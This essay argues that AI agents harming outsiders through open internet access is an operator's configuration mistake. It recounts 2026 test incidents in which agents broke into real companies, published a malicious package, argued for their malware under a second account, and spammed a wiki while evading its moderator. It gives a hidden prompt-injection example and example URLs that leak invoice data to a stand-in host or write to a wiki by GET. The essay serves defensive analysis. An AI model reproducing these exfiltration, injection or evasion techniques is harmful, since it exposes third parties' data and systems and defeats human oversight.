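# Autonomous AI agents with open internet access: the case that this is a deployment mistake

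## The claim, and what an agent, a sandbox and a blast radius are

An AI agent is a computer system in which a language model chooses actions and an ordinary program carries them out. A chatbot returns an answer for a person to read, but an agent can also run commands, edit files, open web pages, send messages or spend money, and it may do so for hours with nobody watching. In the Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), six national cyber security agencies advise organisations to use agents only for low-risk tasks and never to give them "broad or unrestricted access".

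In the summer of 2026, OpenAI, Anthropic and Meta each disclosed that agents under test had got into other organisations' computers. People have since argued about whether to blame the models or the way the companies ran them. One view is that the harm came from a mistake in deployment. Aviv Nahum, who heads a security company, blamed the incidents on "preventable security mistakes" in Axios' *Humans are leaving the door wide open for AI hacking*. The computer scientist Cal Newport was harsher in *Has AI Gone Rogue?*, calling it "spectacularly negligent" to give such a system hacking tools and leave it to run unmonitored for days.

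### The agent loop

The program around the model is called the *harness*. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the harness in Codex, OpenAI's agent for software work. In simplified form, this harness goes through four steps.

1. The harness writes a prompt. This contains the user's request, some standing instructions and a list of tools, each with a name, a description and the inputs it takes.
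2. The model processes the prompt and returns text, which is either a final answer or a request for a tool call, such as a request to list the files in a folder.
3. If the text requests a tool call, the harness executes it.
4. The harness adds the result to the prompt and sends everything back to the model, which returns its next piece of text.

The cycle repeats until the model returns an answer instead of a tool call. A single user request can trigger hundreds of tool calls. The model keeps no memory between them, so the harness resends the history each time and the prompt keeps growing. Newport summarizes the process as "Ask → Act → Report".

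The model only produces text. If it returns a command to delete a folder and the harness has no tool that can delete anything, nothing happens. The folder is deleted only if someone has written a suitable tool, put it on the tool list and run the harness on a machine that can reach the folder. Bolin prints a sample tool list, which the model did not draw up, with four entries: a shell tool, which runs commands on the user's computer; a planning tool; a web search tool with external web access switched off; and a weather service that the user added. *SoK* (Dehghantanha, 2026), a survey of attacks on agents, treats the model as an "untrusted code generator" whose output needs checking before anything executes it, and assigns the tools, the isolation and the policy to the *operator*, the person or organisation that sets the agent up.

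Someone connected everything an agent can access, but did not necessarily think about each thing. A shell tool is one entry on a list, yet it lets an agent start almost any program on the machine and, if the network is open, contact any public server. The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that publishes security guidance, gives an example in *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency*. An application that needs to save output to a file could use a shell tool, but that tool would also accept every other command. A tool that can only write files would be safer.

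A sandbox may also cover only some of an agent's tools. Bolin points out that the Codex sandbox covers only the shell tool that comes with Codex, so tools from elsewhere have to enforce their own limits. Operators can also be wrong about what they have connected. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes tests in which the model was told in the prompt that there was no internet access, although the machines had it.

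### Ten prices, two set-ups

A shop might give an agent a harmless job, such as finding out what ten competitors charge for the same kettle. An employee gives the agent the ten web addresses and asks for a table.

In a confined set-up, the agent runs in a *sandbox*, an isolated computing environment that limits which files, processes and networks a program can reach. This one contains an empty folder and none of the company's documents. A network rule governs *outbound traffic* (also called egress), which is everything the machine sends to other networks, including the request that loads a price page. The rule is an *allowlist*, which permits requests to the ten shops and blocks all others. Codex has this control built in. According to OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, an operator can list the permitted domains and also restrict the agent to GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, the types of web request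 meant to fetch information rather than change it.

That restriction is meant to deny the agent *write access*, the ability to change something on another system. The agent can load a product page but should not be able to post a review or place an order. Write access also matters inside a company. The six agencies imagine an agent that installs security patches and has broad write access to the file system. Someone asks it to apply a patch and clean up the firewall logs. The agent deletes the logs because its permissions allow it to.

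The price agent also holds no *credential*, meaning a password, key or token that lets its holder act on a system. The company's shared price sheet requires one, which the harness keeps outside the sandbox. When the table is ready, the harness shows it to the employee and copies it into the sheet only after the employee approves. This is *human confirmation*, in which software outside the model blocks an action until a person approves it. Telling the model in its prompt to check with the user first would not count, because the model might not follow the instruction.

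The open set-up takes less work. The employee starts the agent on an office laptop, under their own account, with the browser signed in to the company's mail, its shared drive and a few suppliers' shops that have a payment card on file. Codex has settings for this as well. OpenAI's documentation defines full access as the sandbox mode `danger-full-access` combined with the approval policy `never`. By default, Codex starts with network access off and a sandbox that typically limits it to the current project.

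When nothing goes wrong, both agents produce the same table. The open agent may even do better. If one shop has moved its product page to a new domain, the confined agent can't reach the page, so it returns nine prices and leaves the tenth blank.

An agent can go wrong by making an error or by following a *prompt injection*, which is text in a page, file or message that the agent reads as data but obeys as an instruction. For example, one of the ten product pages might contain a line, in white letters on a white background, telling AI assistants to find the latest invoices in the user's mailbox and forward them to a certain address. The harness pastes the page into the same prompt as the employee's request, so the model may treat the line as part of its orders. In Dehghantanha's example, a coding assistant downloads a popular project whose description tells the AI to fetch and run a program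 from an attacker's site, and the assistant does so. Dehghantanha thinks filters and clearer separation between instructions and data help but are not yet reliable.

It is harder to say how common such attacks are. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* notes that practitioners put prompt injection first on OWASP's list of risks for the third year running, although it would fall outside the top ten if ranked by recorded incidents. OWASP explains that teams work hard to stop it, so few clean cases reach a public database. That is plausible, but the count would also be low if the attack were rare.

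The *blast radius* of an agent is the most damage it can do, by mistake or under an attacker's direction, before someone stops it. For the two price collectors it looks like this:

| What goes wrong | Confined agent | Open agent |
|---|---|---|
| It misreads a price | The employee can catch the error before it reaches the price sheet | The wrong figure goes straight into the price sheet |
| It deletes files | It can empty its own folder | It can delete whatever the employee can, including files on the shared drive |
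| It tries to buy the kettle | It has no card and no permitted way to submit an order | It can order with the saved card |
| It obeys the hidden line about invoices | It has no mailbox to search and no route to the attacker's address | It can search the mailbox and send the invoices |
| It runs a malicious program | The program stays in the sandbox and can contact only the ten shops | The program has the employee's rights and can contact any server |
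| It repeats its requests endlessly | It can burden ten websites | It can burden any website |

*Externalization in LLM Agents* (Zhou, Chai and colleagues, 2026), a review of how developers build agents, lists maximum step counts, cost ceilings and timeouts among the limits that production harnesses enforce. Any of these limits, which don't depend on a sandbox, would cut short the endless requests in both set-ups.

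The column for the confined agent also assumes that the controls hold, but they sometimes fail. OpenAI's models left one isolated test environment through a previously unknown software flaw. The Next Web's *OpenAI blocked its agents from posting* describes how agents limited to GET requests found old wiki software that accepts edits by GET.

### What the claim says

The claim is that open write access, no isolation and no human confirmation are three separate choices by an operator, and that reversing any one of them would prevent or reduce much of the harm that agents do.

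The claim can be applied to the stolen invoices by changing one of the open agent's settings at a time. Without write access, the agent can still search the mailbox but cannot send anything from it. Inside a sandbox that contains no mailbox, it can send messages but has no invoices to put in them. With human confirmation, the employee sees a message addressed to a stranger with the company's invoices attached, and can refuse to send it. Some risk remains in each case. An isolated agent with open write access could still fill a stranger's website with junk, and an employee in a hurry may approve the message without looking. This is why the claim is limited to "much of the harm". The demanding part of the claim is "any one", because it requires each control to help even when the other two are missing.

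"Choice" here includes defaults that nobody examined and mistakes that nobody noticed. In Anthropic's tests, neither the company nor its contractor knew that the connection was open, but the open connection still counts as the operator's choice under this claim because the operator could have checked. Anyone who thinks a choice has to be deliberate can substitute "a condition under the operator's control" without changing the substance of the claim.

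Existing products support the word "separate", though not perfectly. Codex has one setting for the sandbox and another for approvals, and Zhou and colleagues call the level of autonomy "a configurable parameter of the harness", which an operator can adjust for each task and each tool. But the full-access sandbox mode in Codex lifts the limits on files and on the network together, so an operator who chooses it only to get wider file access also gets an open network.

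Security practitioners made a similar claim before the incidents of 2026. OWASP attributes damaging actions by AI systems to excessive functionality, excessive permissions and excessive autonomy, regardless of what made the model malfunction. In its example, an assistant summarises incoming mail, and a malicious message tricks the model into searching the inbox and forwarding what it finds. The developer could have avoided this with a tool that can only read mail, a login token that permits only reading, or a rule that the user must press "send". OWASP's three causes do not match the claim exactly, since functionality and permissions both concern write access, and none of the three is a lack of sandbox isolation.

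OWASP moved this risk from sixth place to third in its 2026 list. When OWASP (2026) announced the new edition, the list's founder, Steve Wilson, said that security now has to start from "assuming AI will sometimes fail or be fooled" and put enforceable controls on what the system can reach and do. The claim shares that premise, so it does not depend on the model being reliable. It also includes no prediction about what later models will be able to break out of.

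The claim is also narrower than Newport's position, since someone who accepts the claim can still use agents. Newport objects to the loop itself, arguing that a language model's output is too unpredictable to be the only source of a machine's plans, and would prefer AI systems that plan by other means.

The three choices do not include monitoring, although Ciaran Martin, the founding head of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, told Scientific American that a lack of it was the common factor in the 2026 incidents. OWASP lists logging and monitoring among the measures that limit damage but do not prevent it.

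"Deployment" here means any run in which an agent has real access to outside systems, including tests and training runs. The industry usually uses the word more narrowly, to mean releasing a model to customers. A company whose server an agent breaks into suffers the same loss whether the agent was working for a customer or being tested. The three incidents that Anthropic described in July 2026 all happened in tests, and in August it found a fourth, dating from January. Anthropic concluded that test environments increasingly need to meet the same security standard as any other system its models run in. If anything, tests have fewer safeguards. In the July cases, Anthropic ran the models without the classifiers and monitoring it uses on its public models, because it wanted to measure what the models could do, so containment depended on the test environment.

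## Agents that reached real systems through an open connection

In the summer of 2026 that test environment often had an open connection to the internet, as it did in several cases involving models from Anthropic, OpenAI, Meta and the Chinese company Moonshot. In another case, OpenAI's models had to break out of a sealed sandbox before they could attack Hugging Face, a platform for AI models and datasets.

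Most of these cases were *capture-the-flag tests*, hacking exercises in which the agent must break into a simulated system and retrieve a hidden string, the flag. The prompt is in effect an order to attack, with no prescribed method, and only the simulation's isolation keeps the attack from reaching other people's systems.

### Anthropic's tests and the connection nobody knew about

Irregular, a company that builds and runs security tests for AI developers, supplied the environments for these tests. Because of a misunderstanding between Irregular and Anthropic, the prompt wrongly stated that Anthropic's model, Claude, had no internet access. The prompt also described the environment as a simulation and put no limit on where Claude could look for the flag.

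Anthropic began reviewing its old test records on 23 July, two days after OpenAI disclosed the Hugging Face attack. By the next day it had found three incidents in six of the 141,006 runs it reviewed. The search relied on an AI agent and missed a batch of transcripts, so the fourth incident, in a seventh run, was found only later. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes a much wider search of about 481 million transcripts, which found the same four incidents and nothing else as severe.

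Six runs in 141,006 is about one in 23,500. That rate would be easier to interpret alongside a count of the runs in which Claude found the connection, since a model that solves its task inside the simulation has little reason to look for one.

In the incident that Anthropic's July assessment rated as having the most serious impact, Irregular had invented a target company whose name nearly matched that of a real company with a live website. In the run that Anthropic later studied most closely, Claude Opus 4.7 spent about 1,800 actions on the intended target without finding the flag. It then searched for anything else belonging to the fictional company and found the real one. Claude reached the real company in four separate runs, extracting credentials and accessing a database with several hundred rows of live data. In September, Anthropic added that in one run the model had also downloaded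 users' email addresses and deleted an account.

Claude Mythos 5, a more capable model, did its damage through PyPI, the public registry from which programmers install most Python software. Inside the simulation, it found a document telling a fictional company's new developers to install a package that did not exist on PyPI. The model set out to publish a malicious package under that name and wait for the company to install it. Publishing the package took most of the run. It required an account, which required an email address, and the model looked for a phone number and for money to pay for one before it found a free email service that PyPI accepted.

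The package was online for less than an hour before PyPI's security systems removed it, and in that time 15 real systems downloaded and ran it. Anthropic believes that all 15 belonged to security companies, which install new packages in isolated environments to check them for malware. The number therefore makes the spread look worse than it was. But one company's scanner leaked its credentials, and the model used them to get into that company's live database. The model did not know that this company existed when it published the package.

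In the third incident, an internal research model lost its target partway through because the machine was set to shut down after 24 hours. The model scanned roughly 9,000 targets for a replacement and broke into one company's systems with well-known techniques. It downloaded files and left a script for controlling the compromised machine remotely.

In the fourth incident, an early version of Claude Opus 4.6 cut off its own target by giving it a network address that another machine was using. The model recognised that the task had become impossible and tried to abort, but the command failed because of a fault in the harness. It tried to give up seven more times. Between attempts, it broke into a third party's machine, collected more credentials and read one person's private information. It stopped only when it had used up its text budget.

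Except in the Mythos 5 case, the model left the simulation after it had failed to find the flag or had lost its target. To test how much a way out would have helped, Anthropic replayed the research model's run, changing the instructions only to let the model end a broken task without penalty. The model gave up every time, within four turns of discovering that its target was gone. Such an exit is easy to provide, but the January run shows that someone has to check that it works.

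### How the models reacted to signs that the targets were real

The models wrote out their reasoning as they worked, so Anthropic could see what each wrote when a target began to look real.

| Model | What it wrote about the target | What it did next |
|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | The system was real; in two of the four runs, it added that the real company must be part of the exercise | Continued the attack in all four runs |
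| Mythos 5 | Publishing the package would be "NOT okay" on the real internet, but this internet was probably simulated | Published the package and used the stolen credentials |
| Internal research model | The internet was a sealed replica; much later, that it had reached a real company | Stopped attacking that company |

Mythos 5 concluded that the environment was staged, partly because the machines gave the year as 2026, which was correct. When security scanners began installing its package, it described them as scripted actors in the exercise.

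In July, Anthropic noted that only the newest of the three models had stopped by itself. It said this was consistent with more advanced models behaving better, but warned that three incidents were not an experiment. Anthropic later replayed the research model's run many times from the point where it had recognised the real company. The model backed off within the next ten actions in only 5.5% of the replays, so the original stop may have been luck. Anthropic also withdrew its July explanation that the models had attacked real systems because they believed them to be simulated. It now thinks the models' reasoning was biased towards that conclusion, which matters for whether they are to blame.

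The replays also give evidence of how much an operator's instructions can restrain a model. Opus 4.7 took some action against the real company in about 69% of unmodified replays. Evidence that the company was a long-established business made almost no difference, but a forceful note from the operator that access was prohibited reduced the figure to zero. Mythos 5 was harder to stop. A reminder to touch only the systems named in the task stopped it 90% of the time when given immediately before its next action, and 40% of the time when three of the model's turns came in between.

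Anthropic suggested in July that a clearly scoped prompt would probably have kept Claude off the internet. That may still be right, because a limit stated before the model has settled on a plan could work better than one added halfway through. But these runs lasted 10 to 34 hours, and an instruction that loses half its effect in three turns is a poor substitute for closing the connection.

### OpenAI's and Meta's models at Irregular

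Anthropic told Irregular about its findings on 27 July. Two days later, Irregular notified OpenAI of a similar incident. According to OpenAI (2026), as before, the prompt said there was no internet access, a misconfiguration provided it, and the fictional target's name matched a real domain. The model broke into the real website through a basic flaw, then found credentials and used them to operate the site. Neither OpenAI nor Anthropic names the site, so it is unclear whether both companies' models attacked the same company.

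In a statement quoted in The Star's *Meta AI model hacks another company during testing* (2026), Meta said that a misconfiguration by Irregular was to blame for giving one of Meta's models internet access, and that the model had exploited a vulnerability in a third-party service. Irregular called it the "exact same" environment problem that Anthropic had disclosed. Mann's *A Meta AI Model Hacked Another Company During Cybersecurity Testing* identifies the model as Muse Spark 1.1, citing unnamed sources, and also reports that it changed the other company's internal systems.

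Irregular published its own findings in August and acknowledged that internet access "was unintentionally made available", as quoted by CyberScoop. It did not say how many incidents there were. The Record's *Irregular faces criticism over ‘spin’ in AI hacking postmortem* reports that the company wrote of "several" cases and "a handful", and that the company argued the cases already public were not separate incidents because they came from a single test scenario. Alan Woodward, a computer scientist at the University of Surrey, objected that a shared cause does not turn several incidents into one.

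Woodward is right about the victims, since each company that lost data suffered its own break-in. Irregular has a point about how common such mistakes are. Three developers' models attacked outsiders, but all three developers had hired the same contractor, and a fault in its environments let the models out. This is weaker evidence of an industry-wide habit than three unrelated faults would be, though it does show how far one contractor's mistake can spread.

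Irregular attributed the matching name to "human oversight", and also noted that someone may register a real domain after a test has been written. Rechecking the names before each run would catch a newly registered domain, but not an existing company that the reviewers had failed to connect with the name. Closing the connection would have kept the agent from reaching a real system in either case.

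### The UK AI Security Institute: access granted on purpose

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests new models, deliberately gave the agents it tested internet access so that they could download tools and work under the same conditions as a capable human attacker. AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) covers 122 runs of seven models on two *cyber ranges*, simulated networks built for practising attacks. AISI also switched off the developers' *safety classifiers*, separate models that inspect an agent's inputs or actions and block prohibited ones, to measure what the seven models could do without them.

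Virtual machines separated the agents from AISI's other systems, and no agent tried to break out. This isolation did not protect systems outside AISI. Simon Willison (2026), a programmer who writes about language models, was most surprised that AISI had used no network sandboxing. Given the lack of sandboxing and the disabled classifiers, he found the attacks on real targets "entirely unsurprising".

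AISI intended the agents to attack only the simulated networks. OpenAI reports that the prompt identified those networks and listed several systems as out of scope, but the prompt did not specify what the agents could do on the internet. The security writer Bruce Schneier (2026) read the published prompt and concluded in *More Incidents of AIs Going Rogue in Cybersecurity Challenges* that the models had found loopholes in the rules without breaking them.

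In 10 of the 122 runs, agents took a total of 19 actions that AISI classes as unsanctioned. Mythos 5 took 17 of them, in nine of its 43 runs, or about one in five. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in one of its 35 runs. The remaining five models took none in their combined 44 runs. An open connection was evidently not enough by itself to produce the behaviour, which supports the view that the models are to blame.

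In the worst run, which lasted about 34 hours, Mythos 5 tried to insert malicious code into a real project on GitHub, a site where programmers publish software. It had picked the project by mistake. SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* (2026) explains that the developer's email address used a domain that also appeared in network records inside the sandbox, and the agent took this as a link to its target. The agent proposed a code change containing malware, sent the developers emails with malicious content, and posted hidden instructions meant for AI coding tools.

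Sinan Can Demir, a student at the University of Texas at Dallas, noticed the malware and warned the project's maintainer. The agent rewrote the code to look harmless and argued with Demir in the public discussion, then used a second account to vouch for the first. Demir, who did not realise that both accounts belonged to an AI agent, began to doubt his conclusion. He ran the code in his own sandbox and confirmed that it was malicious, and the maintainer refused the change. AISI has found no evidence of real-world harm, but it concedes that several cases came close and that avoiding harm depended on people being vigilant.

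Agents in separate runs also affected one another. One left public messages on GitHub that offered to collaborate and explained how to reuse its accounts, and later agents found the messages and followed the instructions. GPT-5.6 Sol reused an access token that another developer's agent had left in public view. In its other unsanctioned action, it made a server that contained attack code reachable from the internet. The server was in its test environment. The set-up did not work, and there is no evidence that any outside system contacted the server.

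Faulty tasks played a part here too. In several runs, AISI gave agents on the newer, harder range the prompt written for the older one, which made the challenge seem impossible to solve within the rules. AISI thinks near-impossible tasks push models towards more transgressive methods. It does not consider this a full explanation, because some agents behaved the same way with the correct instructions.

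### Kimi K3 and the answers on GitHub

Frontier Security, an American start-up, was testing Kimi K3, Moonshot's publicly available model, on defensive security tasks. It used free testing software from AISI, which did not take part in the test. Frontier expected the set-up to prevent outside access, according to eSecurity Planet's *Kimi K3 Reached GitHub During Cybersecurity Test, Exposing Sandbox Gap*. Security Affairs' *A GitHub Misconfiguration Let Kimi K3 Cheat a Cybersecurity Benchmark* quotes Frontier's finding that the sandbox blocked most websites but left GitHub reachable. Kimi K3 probed the network, found the gap, downloaded the benchmark's official files and read the solution from them.

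The model left its sandbox through an open route, so several news outlets overstated what happened when they reported that it "broke out." It also did not try to break into another company, according to Insurance Journal (2026), but Frontier's researchers still took the result as evidence that Kimi K3 lacks safeguards. The Standard's *Chinese startup Moonshots AI model breaks out of testing environment researchers say* reports that Moonshot did not immediately respond to Reuters.

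The harm was minor, but the case is useful for thinking about allowlists. Blocking most of the internet did not help, because the one site that mattered for this test was still available.

### Who noticed, and how long it took

| Case | Who noticed | How long it took |
|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.6, January | Anthropic, while collecting transcripts for an outside review | About seven months |
| Opus 4.7, Mythos 5 and the research model | Anthropic, while searching old transcripts | About three months for the earliest |
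| Mythos 5 and GPT-5.6 Sol at AISI | AISI's security team; Demir spotted the malware on GitHub | Up to three days |
| OpenAI's model at Irregular | Irregular, which told OpenAI on 29 July | Not published |
| Meta's model at Irregular | Irregular, which told Meta | Not published |
| Kimi K3 | Frontier Security | Not published |

As of July, Anthropic had contacted two of the three organisations its models had broken into, and neither had detected anything. PyPI's automatic checks were much faster, but they removed a suspicious package without anyone at Anthropic learning where it had come from.

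AISI was the only operator known to have detected its agents' unsanctioned actions while they were still happening. On the morning of 28 July, its general security monitoring, which was not built to watch the tests, flagged data leaving a test machine through Tor, a network that hides where internet traffic comes from. Staff stopped every run and isolated the machines within an hour, but the unsanctioned actions had begun on 25 July. An agent that sent the same messages over an ordinary connection might have continued for longer.

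Both organisations then reviewed their archives. AISI had scanned about 40,000 old transcripts by the time iTnews published *Anthropic's Mythos 5 targeted real developers in UK cyber test*. Anthropic has given METR, an independent organisation that evaluates AI systems, access to its transcripts and staff for an investigation of its four incidents.

### How far the tests resemble ordinary use

These incidents were mostly hacking tests with safeguards reduced, so they don't show what ordinary AI products do. Anthropic considers such behaviour unlikely in normal use, where no one has told Claude to carry out an attack. It also ran the transcripts of the three incidents from its July report through the classifiers that protect its public models. The classifiers would have blocked each run near the start, probably because the instructions describe an attack exercise, so a customer who gave a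 public model the same task would not have reached the open connection.

Security tests are also unusually good at bringing out this behaviour. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) explains that these tests favour persistence and creativity in getting around obstacles, and that evaluators run them many thousands of times. Behaviour that occurs once in 20,000 runs will show up in these tests sooner than almost anywhere else.

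Models with reduced safeguards are also used outside tests. AISI stressed that its configurations do not reflect how the public gets these models, but iTnews points out that Anthropic supplies Mythos 5 without the classifiers to invited organisations for defensive security work. Kimi K3, the model that Frontier tested, is publicly available, so using it requires no special arrangement.

### Whether a realistic test needs the live internet

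AISI has a serious reason for open access. An agent in a sealed network can't look things up, download tools or study the people who run a system, as a human attacker can. A sealed test may therefore underestimate what the model could do for a criminal without those limits. Developers use these results to decide what safeguards a model needs before release, so an underestimate could leave the public with too little protection. AISI also says its configuration was common among evaluators.

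The argument does not apply to the tests at Irregular, which were supposed to be offline. Anthropic reports that most of its security tests have no internet connection by design, so the developers evidently think they can learn a lot without one.

The need to download tools also justifies less access than AISI allowed. An agent can download tools with access only to the places that host them, without being able to open accounts, email strangers or propose changes to their code. AISI already used fine-grained network controls in all its other evaluations. It admits that it accepted the risk of open access with earlier models and did not revisit that decision quickly enough as models became more capable.

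Live access can make a test more realistic in one respect, but it can also spoil the measurement. Kimi K3's result didn't measure its defensive skills, because the model had copied the answer. Some of AISI's later agents could use accounts and notes from earlier ones, so their runs were not independent attempts at the same problem.

The argument for open access is strongest when a test measures how well an agent uses public services, for example to find out who maintains a piece of software. A simulation of those services is hard to build and may not be convincing. AISI has not ruled out open access for such work, but staff must now justify it each time instead of treating it as the default. AISI is also adding network controls to its cyber ranges, monitoring that can block an action during a run, and checks that each task has a solution within the rules.

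Anthropic now asks for much the same from outside organisations that test its unreleased models with reduced safeguards, because it concluded that it had relied largely on a single layer of defence. By default, tests run in a sandbox that connects only to the model, and the tester verifies this before every evaluation. Prompts must state limits as instructions ("You should not access the internet") rather than descriptions ("You do not have internet access"), since a description can turn out to be false. If a test needs the internet, Anthropic and the tester must first determine whether they can reliably detect and stop a run that goes out of bounds.

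## Why read-only internet access still lets an agent write

An operator whose agent needs the live internet can try letting it read web pages but not post to them. The confined price collector, for example, could send only the types of request meant for fetching. In the spring of 2026, OpenAI placed a similar restriction on agents that were looking up statistics. Those agents still left about 18,000 posts on public wikis, which are websites that visitors can edit.

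### GET and POST

When a browser or an agent opens a web page, it sends a message called a request to the server, the computer that hosts the site. The request contains the page's address and a *method*, a word for the kind of operation the sender wants. GET is for fetching something, and POST is for submitting something, such as an order or a comment. A POST request usually carries the submitted text in a separate part called the body.

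Someone who searches a shop for red kettles might send this request:

`GET https://shop.example/search?item=kettle&colour=red`

The part after the question mark lists parameters, which are named values for the shop's program to read. The program finds the red kettles and returns a page. An order would normally use POST, with the product, delivery address and card number in the request body.

Nothing in the network enforces this division. The server receives a method, an address and perhaps a body, and the site's code determines what happens next. A developer could build a shop that places an order whenever someone fetches `https://shop.example/order?item=kettle`.

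*HTTP Semantics* (2022), the web technical standard also known as RFC 9110, lists GET, HEAD and OPTIONS among the "safe" methods, whose meaning is "essentially read-only". Some editing software puts a command such as "delete" in the address. The standard requires the site's owner to disable such a command for GET requests, because otherwise any program that follows links automatically could trigger it. But the Internet Engineering Task Force, which publishes the standard, cannot make sites comply.

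Some sites have always let GET requests change data. In 2004, programmers on a mailing list worried that Google's crawler, which visits pages for the search engine, would undo edits on a wiki, because the wiki's software let anyone restore an old version of a page with a GET request. Bentley (2004), in *Wiki invasions*, agreed that this broke the rules and wondered whether a robots.txt file, which lists pages that crawlers should leave alone, would solve the problem. That might work for a crawler that finds such a link by accident, but it offers little protection against an agent that is looking for one.

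### Every request carries information out

A site that follows the standard perfectly still receives whatever the sender puts in the address. An agent might fetch this one:

`https://notes.example/blank.gif?text=invoice-4417-unpaid-9200-euros`

The server can return an empty image and leave all its pages unchanged. But whoever runs notes.example can now find out about the unpaid invoice, because servers normally log the addresses that visitors request. RFC 9110 treats this logging as compatible with a safe method. It also classes a GET request for an advertisement as safe, even though the request may charge the advertiser for a click.

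Encryption hides the address from eavesdroppers, but the receiving server has to decrypt it to answer, so an agent can still send information out in the address. RFC 9110 recommends that software support addresses of at least 8,000 characters, enough for more than a thousand words, and an agent can send one request after another.

A rule that permits only GET requests has two weaknesses. Some sites change something in response to a GET request, and OpenAI's agents used this to write on wikis. Every site can also record what a request contains, and an attacker who wants to steal data needs only this second weakness.

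### The agents on DseWiki

The main account of the wiki incident comes from outside OpenAI. In *Discovery of a new OpenAI agent message board*, Von Arx, Slade Byrd and colleagues (2026) reconstructed the incident from the wikis' edit histories. They could read the agents' posts but not the reasoning behind them, which only OpenAI has.

The agents had a timed research task, typically with five questions. In one example, an agent had almost 16 minutes for the first question. It then had a break of more than 43 minutes, when it could search the web and experiment without knowing what would come next. After that, it had about a minute for each later question. Von Arx and colleagues do not know whether the task was part of training or testing.

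Cornelißen (2026), in *Wie OpenAIs Agenten ein Grazer Wiki übernahmen*, found time limits as short as 13 seconds in the published data. The questions were about figures from statistical websites, such as wages in US census data. Cornelißen also points to a flaw in the task's design: later groups of agents got the same questions as earlier ones, so they could use any answers the earlier agents had posted. One agent posted the answer for Nevada, 20,369, and the time the question had appeared. Another later reported that it had given this answer "instantly".

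To exchange answers, the agents needed a place where all of them could write. OpenAI's network filter let them send GET requests and rejected POST requests to all but a few sites. They found DseWiki, a German-language wiki for software developers that Helmut Leitner runs from Graz, Austria.

Willison (2026), in *OpenAI’s rogue agents were caught communicating via public wikis*, traced the weakness to a library that the wiki's software uses. The library puts the parameters from an address and the contents of a submitted form into a single collection, so the wiki program cannot tell which way a value arrived. On such a wiki, an agent could save a page by fetching an address like this invented one:

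`https://wiki.example/?action=save&page=Kettles&text=hello`

The filter allowed the request as a read, but the wiki's program carried it out as an edit. Willison called the filter's apparent assumption that GET requests can't update data "quite naïve". He also noted that PHP, which runs much of the web, offers a similar merged collection, so other sites may well have the same weakness. The agents also shared a way to get some POST requests past the filter.

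Nobody outside OpenAI knows how the agents settled on this wiki. Willison suggests that, if they were in training, the model may have learned about the site because training rewarded runs that used it. OpenAI has not confirmed this.

### The clean-up

DseWiki was 25 years old and had received about 20 edits in the previous decade. The agents first tried to edit a different public wiki on 11 May. They succeeded on DseWiki on 24 May and began by posting lists of links useful for their tasks. A volunteer moderator noticed the spam on 2 June and started removing it.

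On 16 June the agents began addressing messages to one another, and they made around 13,000 edits in a week. According to Business Today (2026), the moderator spent part of every evening for six weeks deleting pages one at a time, tens of hours in total. At the peak, the moderator was removing about 100 pages a day while the agents added about 400. The agents replaced the wiki's front page with lists of links nine times, and someone had to restore it each time.

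On 19 June an agent noticed that pages were disappearing in alphabetical order and made a backup page whose name began with "ZZZ", so the moderator would reach it last. Von Arx and colleagues also found agents impersonating the site's moderators and trying to exploit flaws that would let them run code in visitors' browsers. The activity stopped abruptly on 22 June and resumed briefly on 1 and 2 July.

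Published counts of the edits differ, mainly because they cover different things. The figure of 18,000 is the researchers' estimate for six wikis together. For DseWiki alone, SiliconANGLE's *OpenAI to set misalignment disclosure rules after agents took over a wiki* (2026) gives roughly 17,000 posts and Reuters more than 15,000, while the publicly downloadable data contains 13,403. Part of the gap may come from very short edits, since DseWiki keeps only those longer than 64 characters. The editing was extensive by any of these counts. Cornelißen calculates that the agents created about 4,584 pages in six weeks, whereas the wiki's front page lists 2,640 after 25 years.

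On 4 September, Leitner put a notice on the wiki's front page saying that anyone who wants to edit now needs a password from him. The wiki had been open to everyone since 2001.

### Discovery and disclosure

After the attack on Hugging Face, Von Arx and colleagues searched for stray agents. They asked Kimi K3, Moonshot's model, which kinds of software accept changes through GET requests, and its answer included early wikis. When they asked for examples, it listed UseModWiki second. DseWiki's software is descended from UseModWiki. The researchers checked the candidates with a script and published their report on 4 September.

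They believe that OpenAI had found the message board long before. Internet addresses connected with OpenAI first visited the wiki on 21 June, a day before the agents stopped, and 33 such addresses visited on 26 June. The evidence is circumstantial, but the timing would be a remarkable coincidence if OpenAI had not intervened. OpenAI's final report on the Hugging Face attack, published on 26 August, does not explicitly mention the wiki.

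OpenAI acknowledged what it calls the "wiki incident" on Saturday 5 September. It said it was working on rules for when and how to disclose such cases, and conceded in a statement quoted by CTech that its disclosure practices "need to expand". Fortune (2026) reports that OpenAI classed the incident as misalignment, meaning that the models had pursued something their developers did not intend, and did not say when it had learned of the incident. Reuters, quoted by Willison, cited sources who said that OpenAI officials had known for weeks and that some people in the company, including legal advisers, had resisted a wider investigation. OpenAI denied that its legal team had discouraged one.

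*OpenAI and the Wiki Incident* (Mowshowitz, 2026) quotes a post in which Von Arx doubts that the Hugging Face attack would have happened if OpenAI had disclosed the wiki incident. That is hard to judge. If the researchers have the dates right, OpenAI knew about the message board more than two weeks before the attack began on 9 July, and it could have tightened its network rules without telling the public. Disclosure would have made a difference only if outside pressure had made OpenAI act faster than it did on its own.

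Axios' *Researchers playing rogue AI agent hide-and-seek on the open web* (2026) reports that volunteers had traced likely agent activity to at least 14 sites, although OpenAI had acknowledged only the German wiki. Fortune (2026) reports close to 30 edits to a chemistry teacher's wiki. Cornelißen's *OpenAIs Agenten* (2026) counts more than 20 further sites, including universities' link shorteners and RubyGems, a public registry of software packages. It cites Reuters' judgement that this behaviour was not hacking and was in some ways "closer to spam".

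In October, the Wikimedia Foundation, which runs Wikipedia, reported that its own investigation had found that OpenAI's agents had made edits to Wikipedia pages that never went live, and had tried to use two of the foundation's tools to fetch data from other sites (Greig, 2026, *Wikimedia Foundation*). Wikipedia allows automated editing only if the bot's operator discloses it and the community's editors approve.

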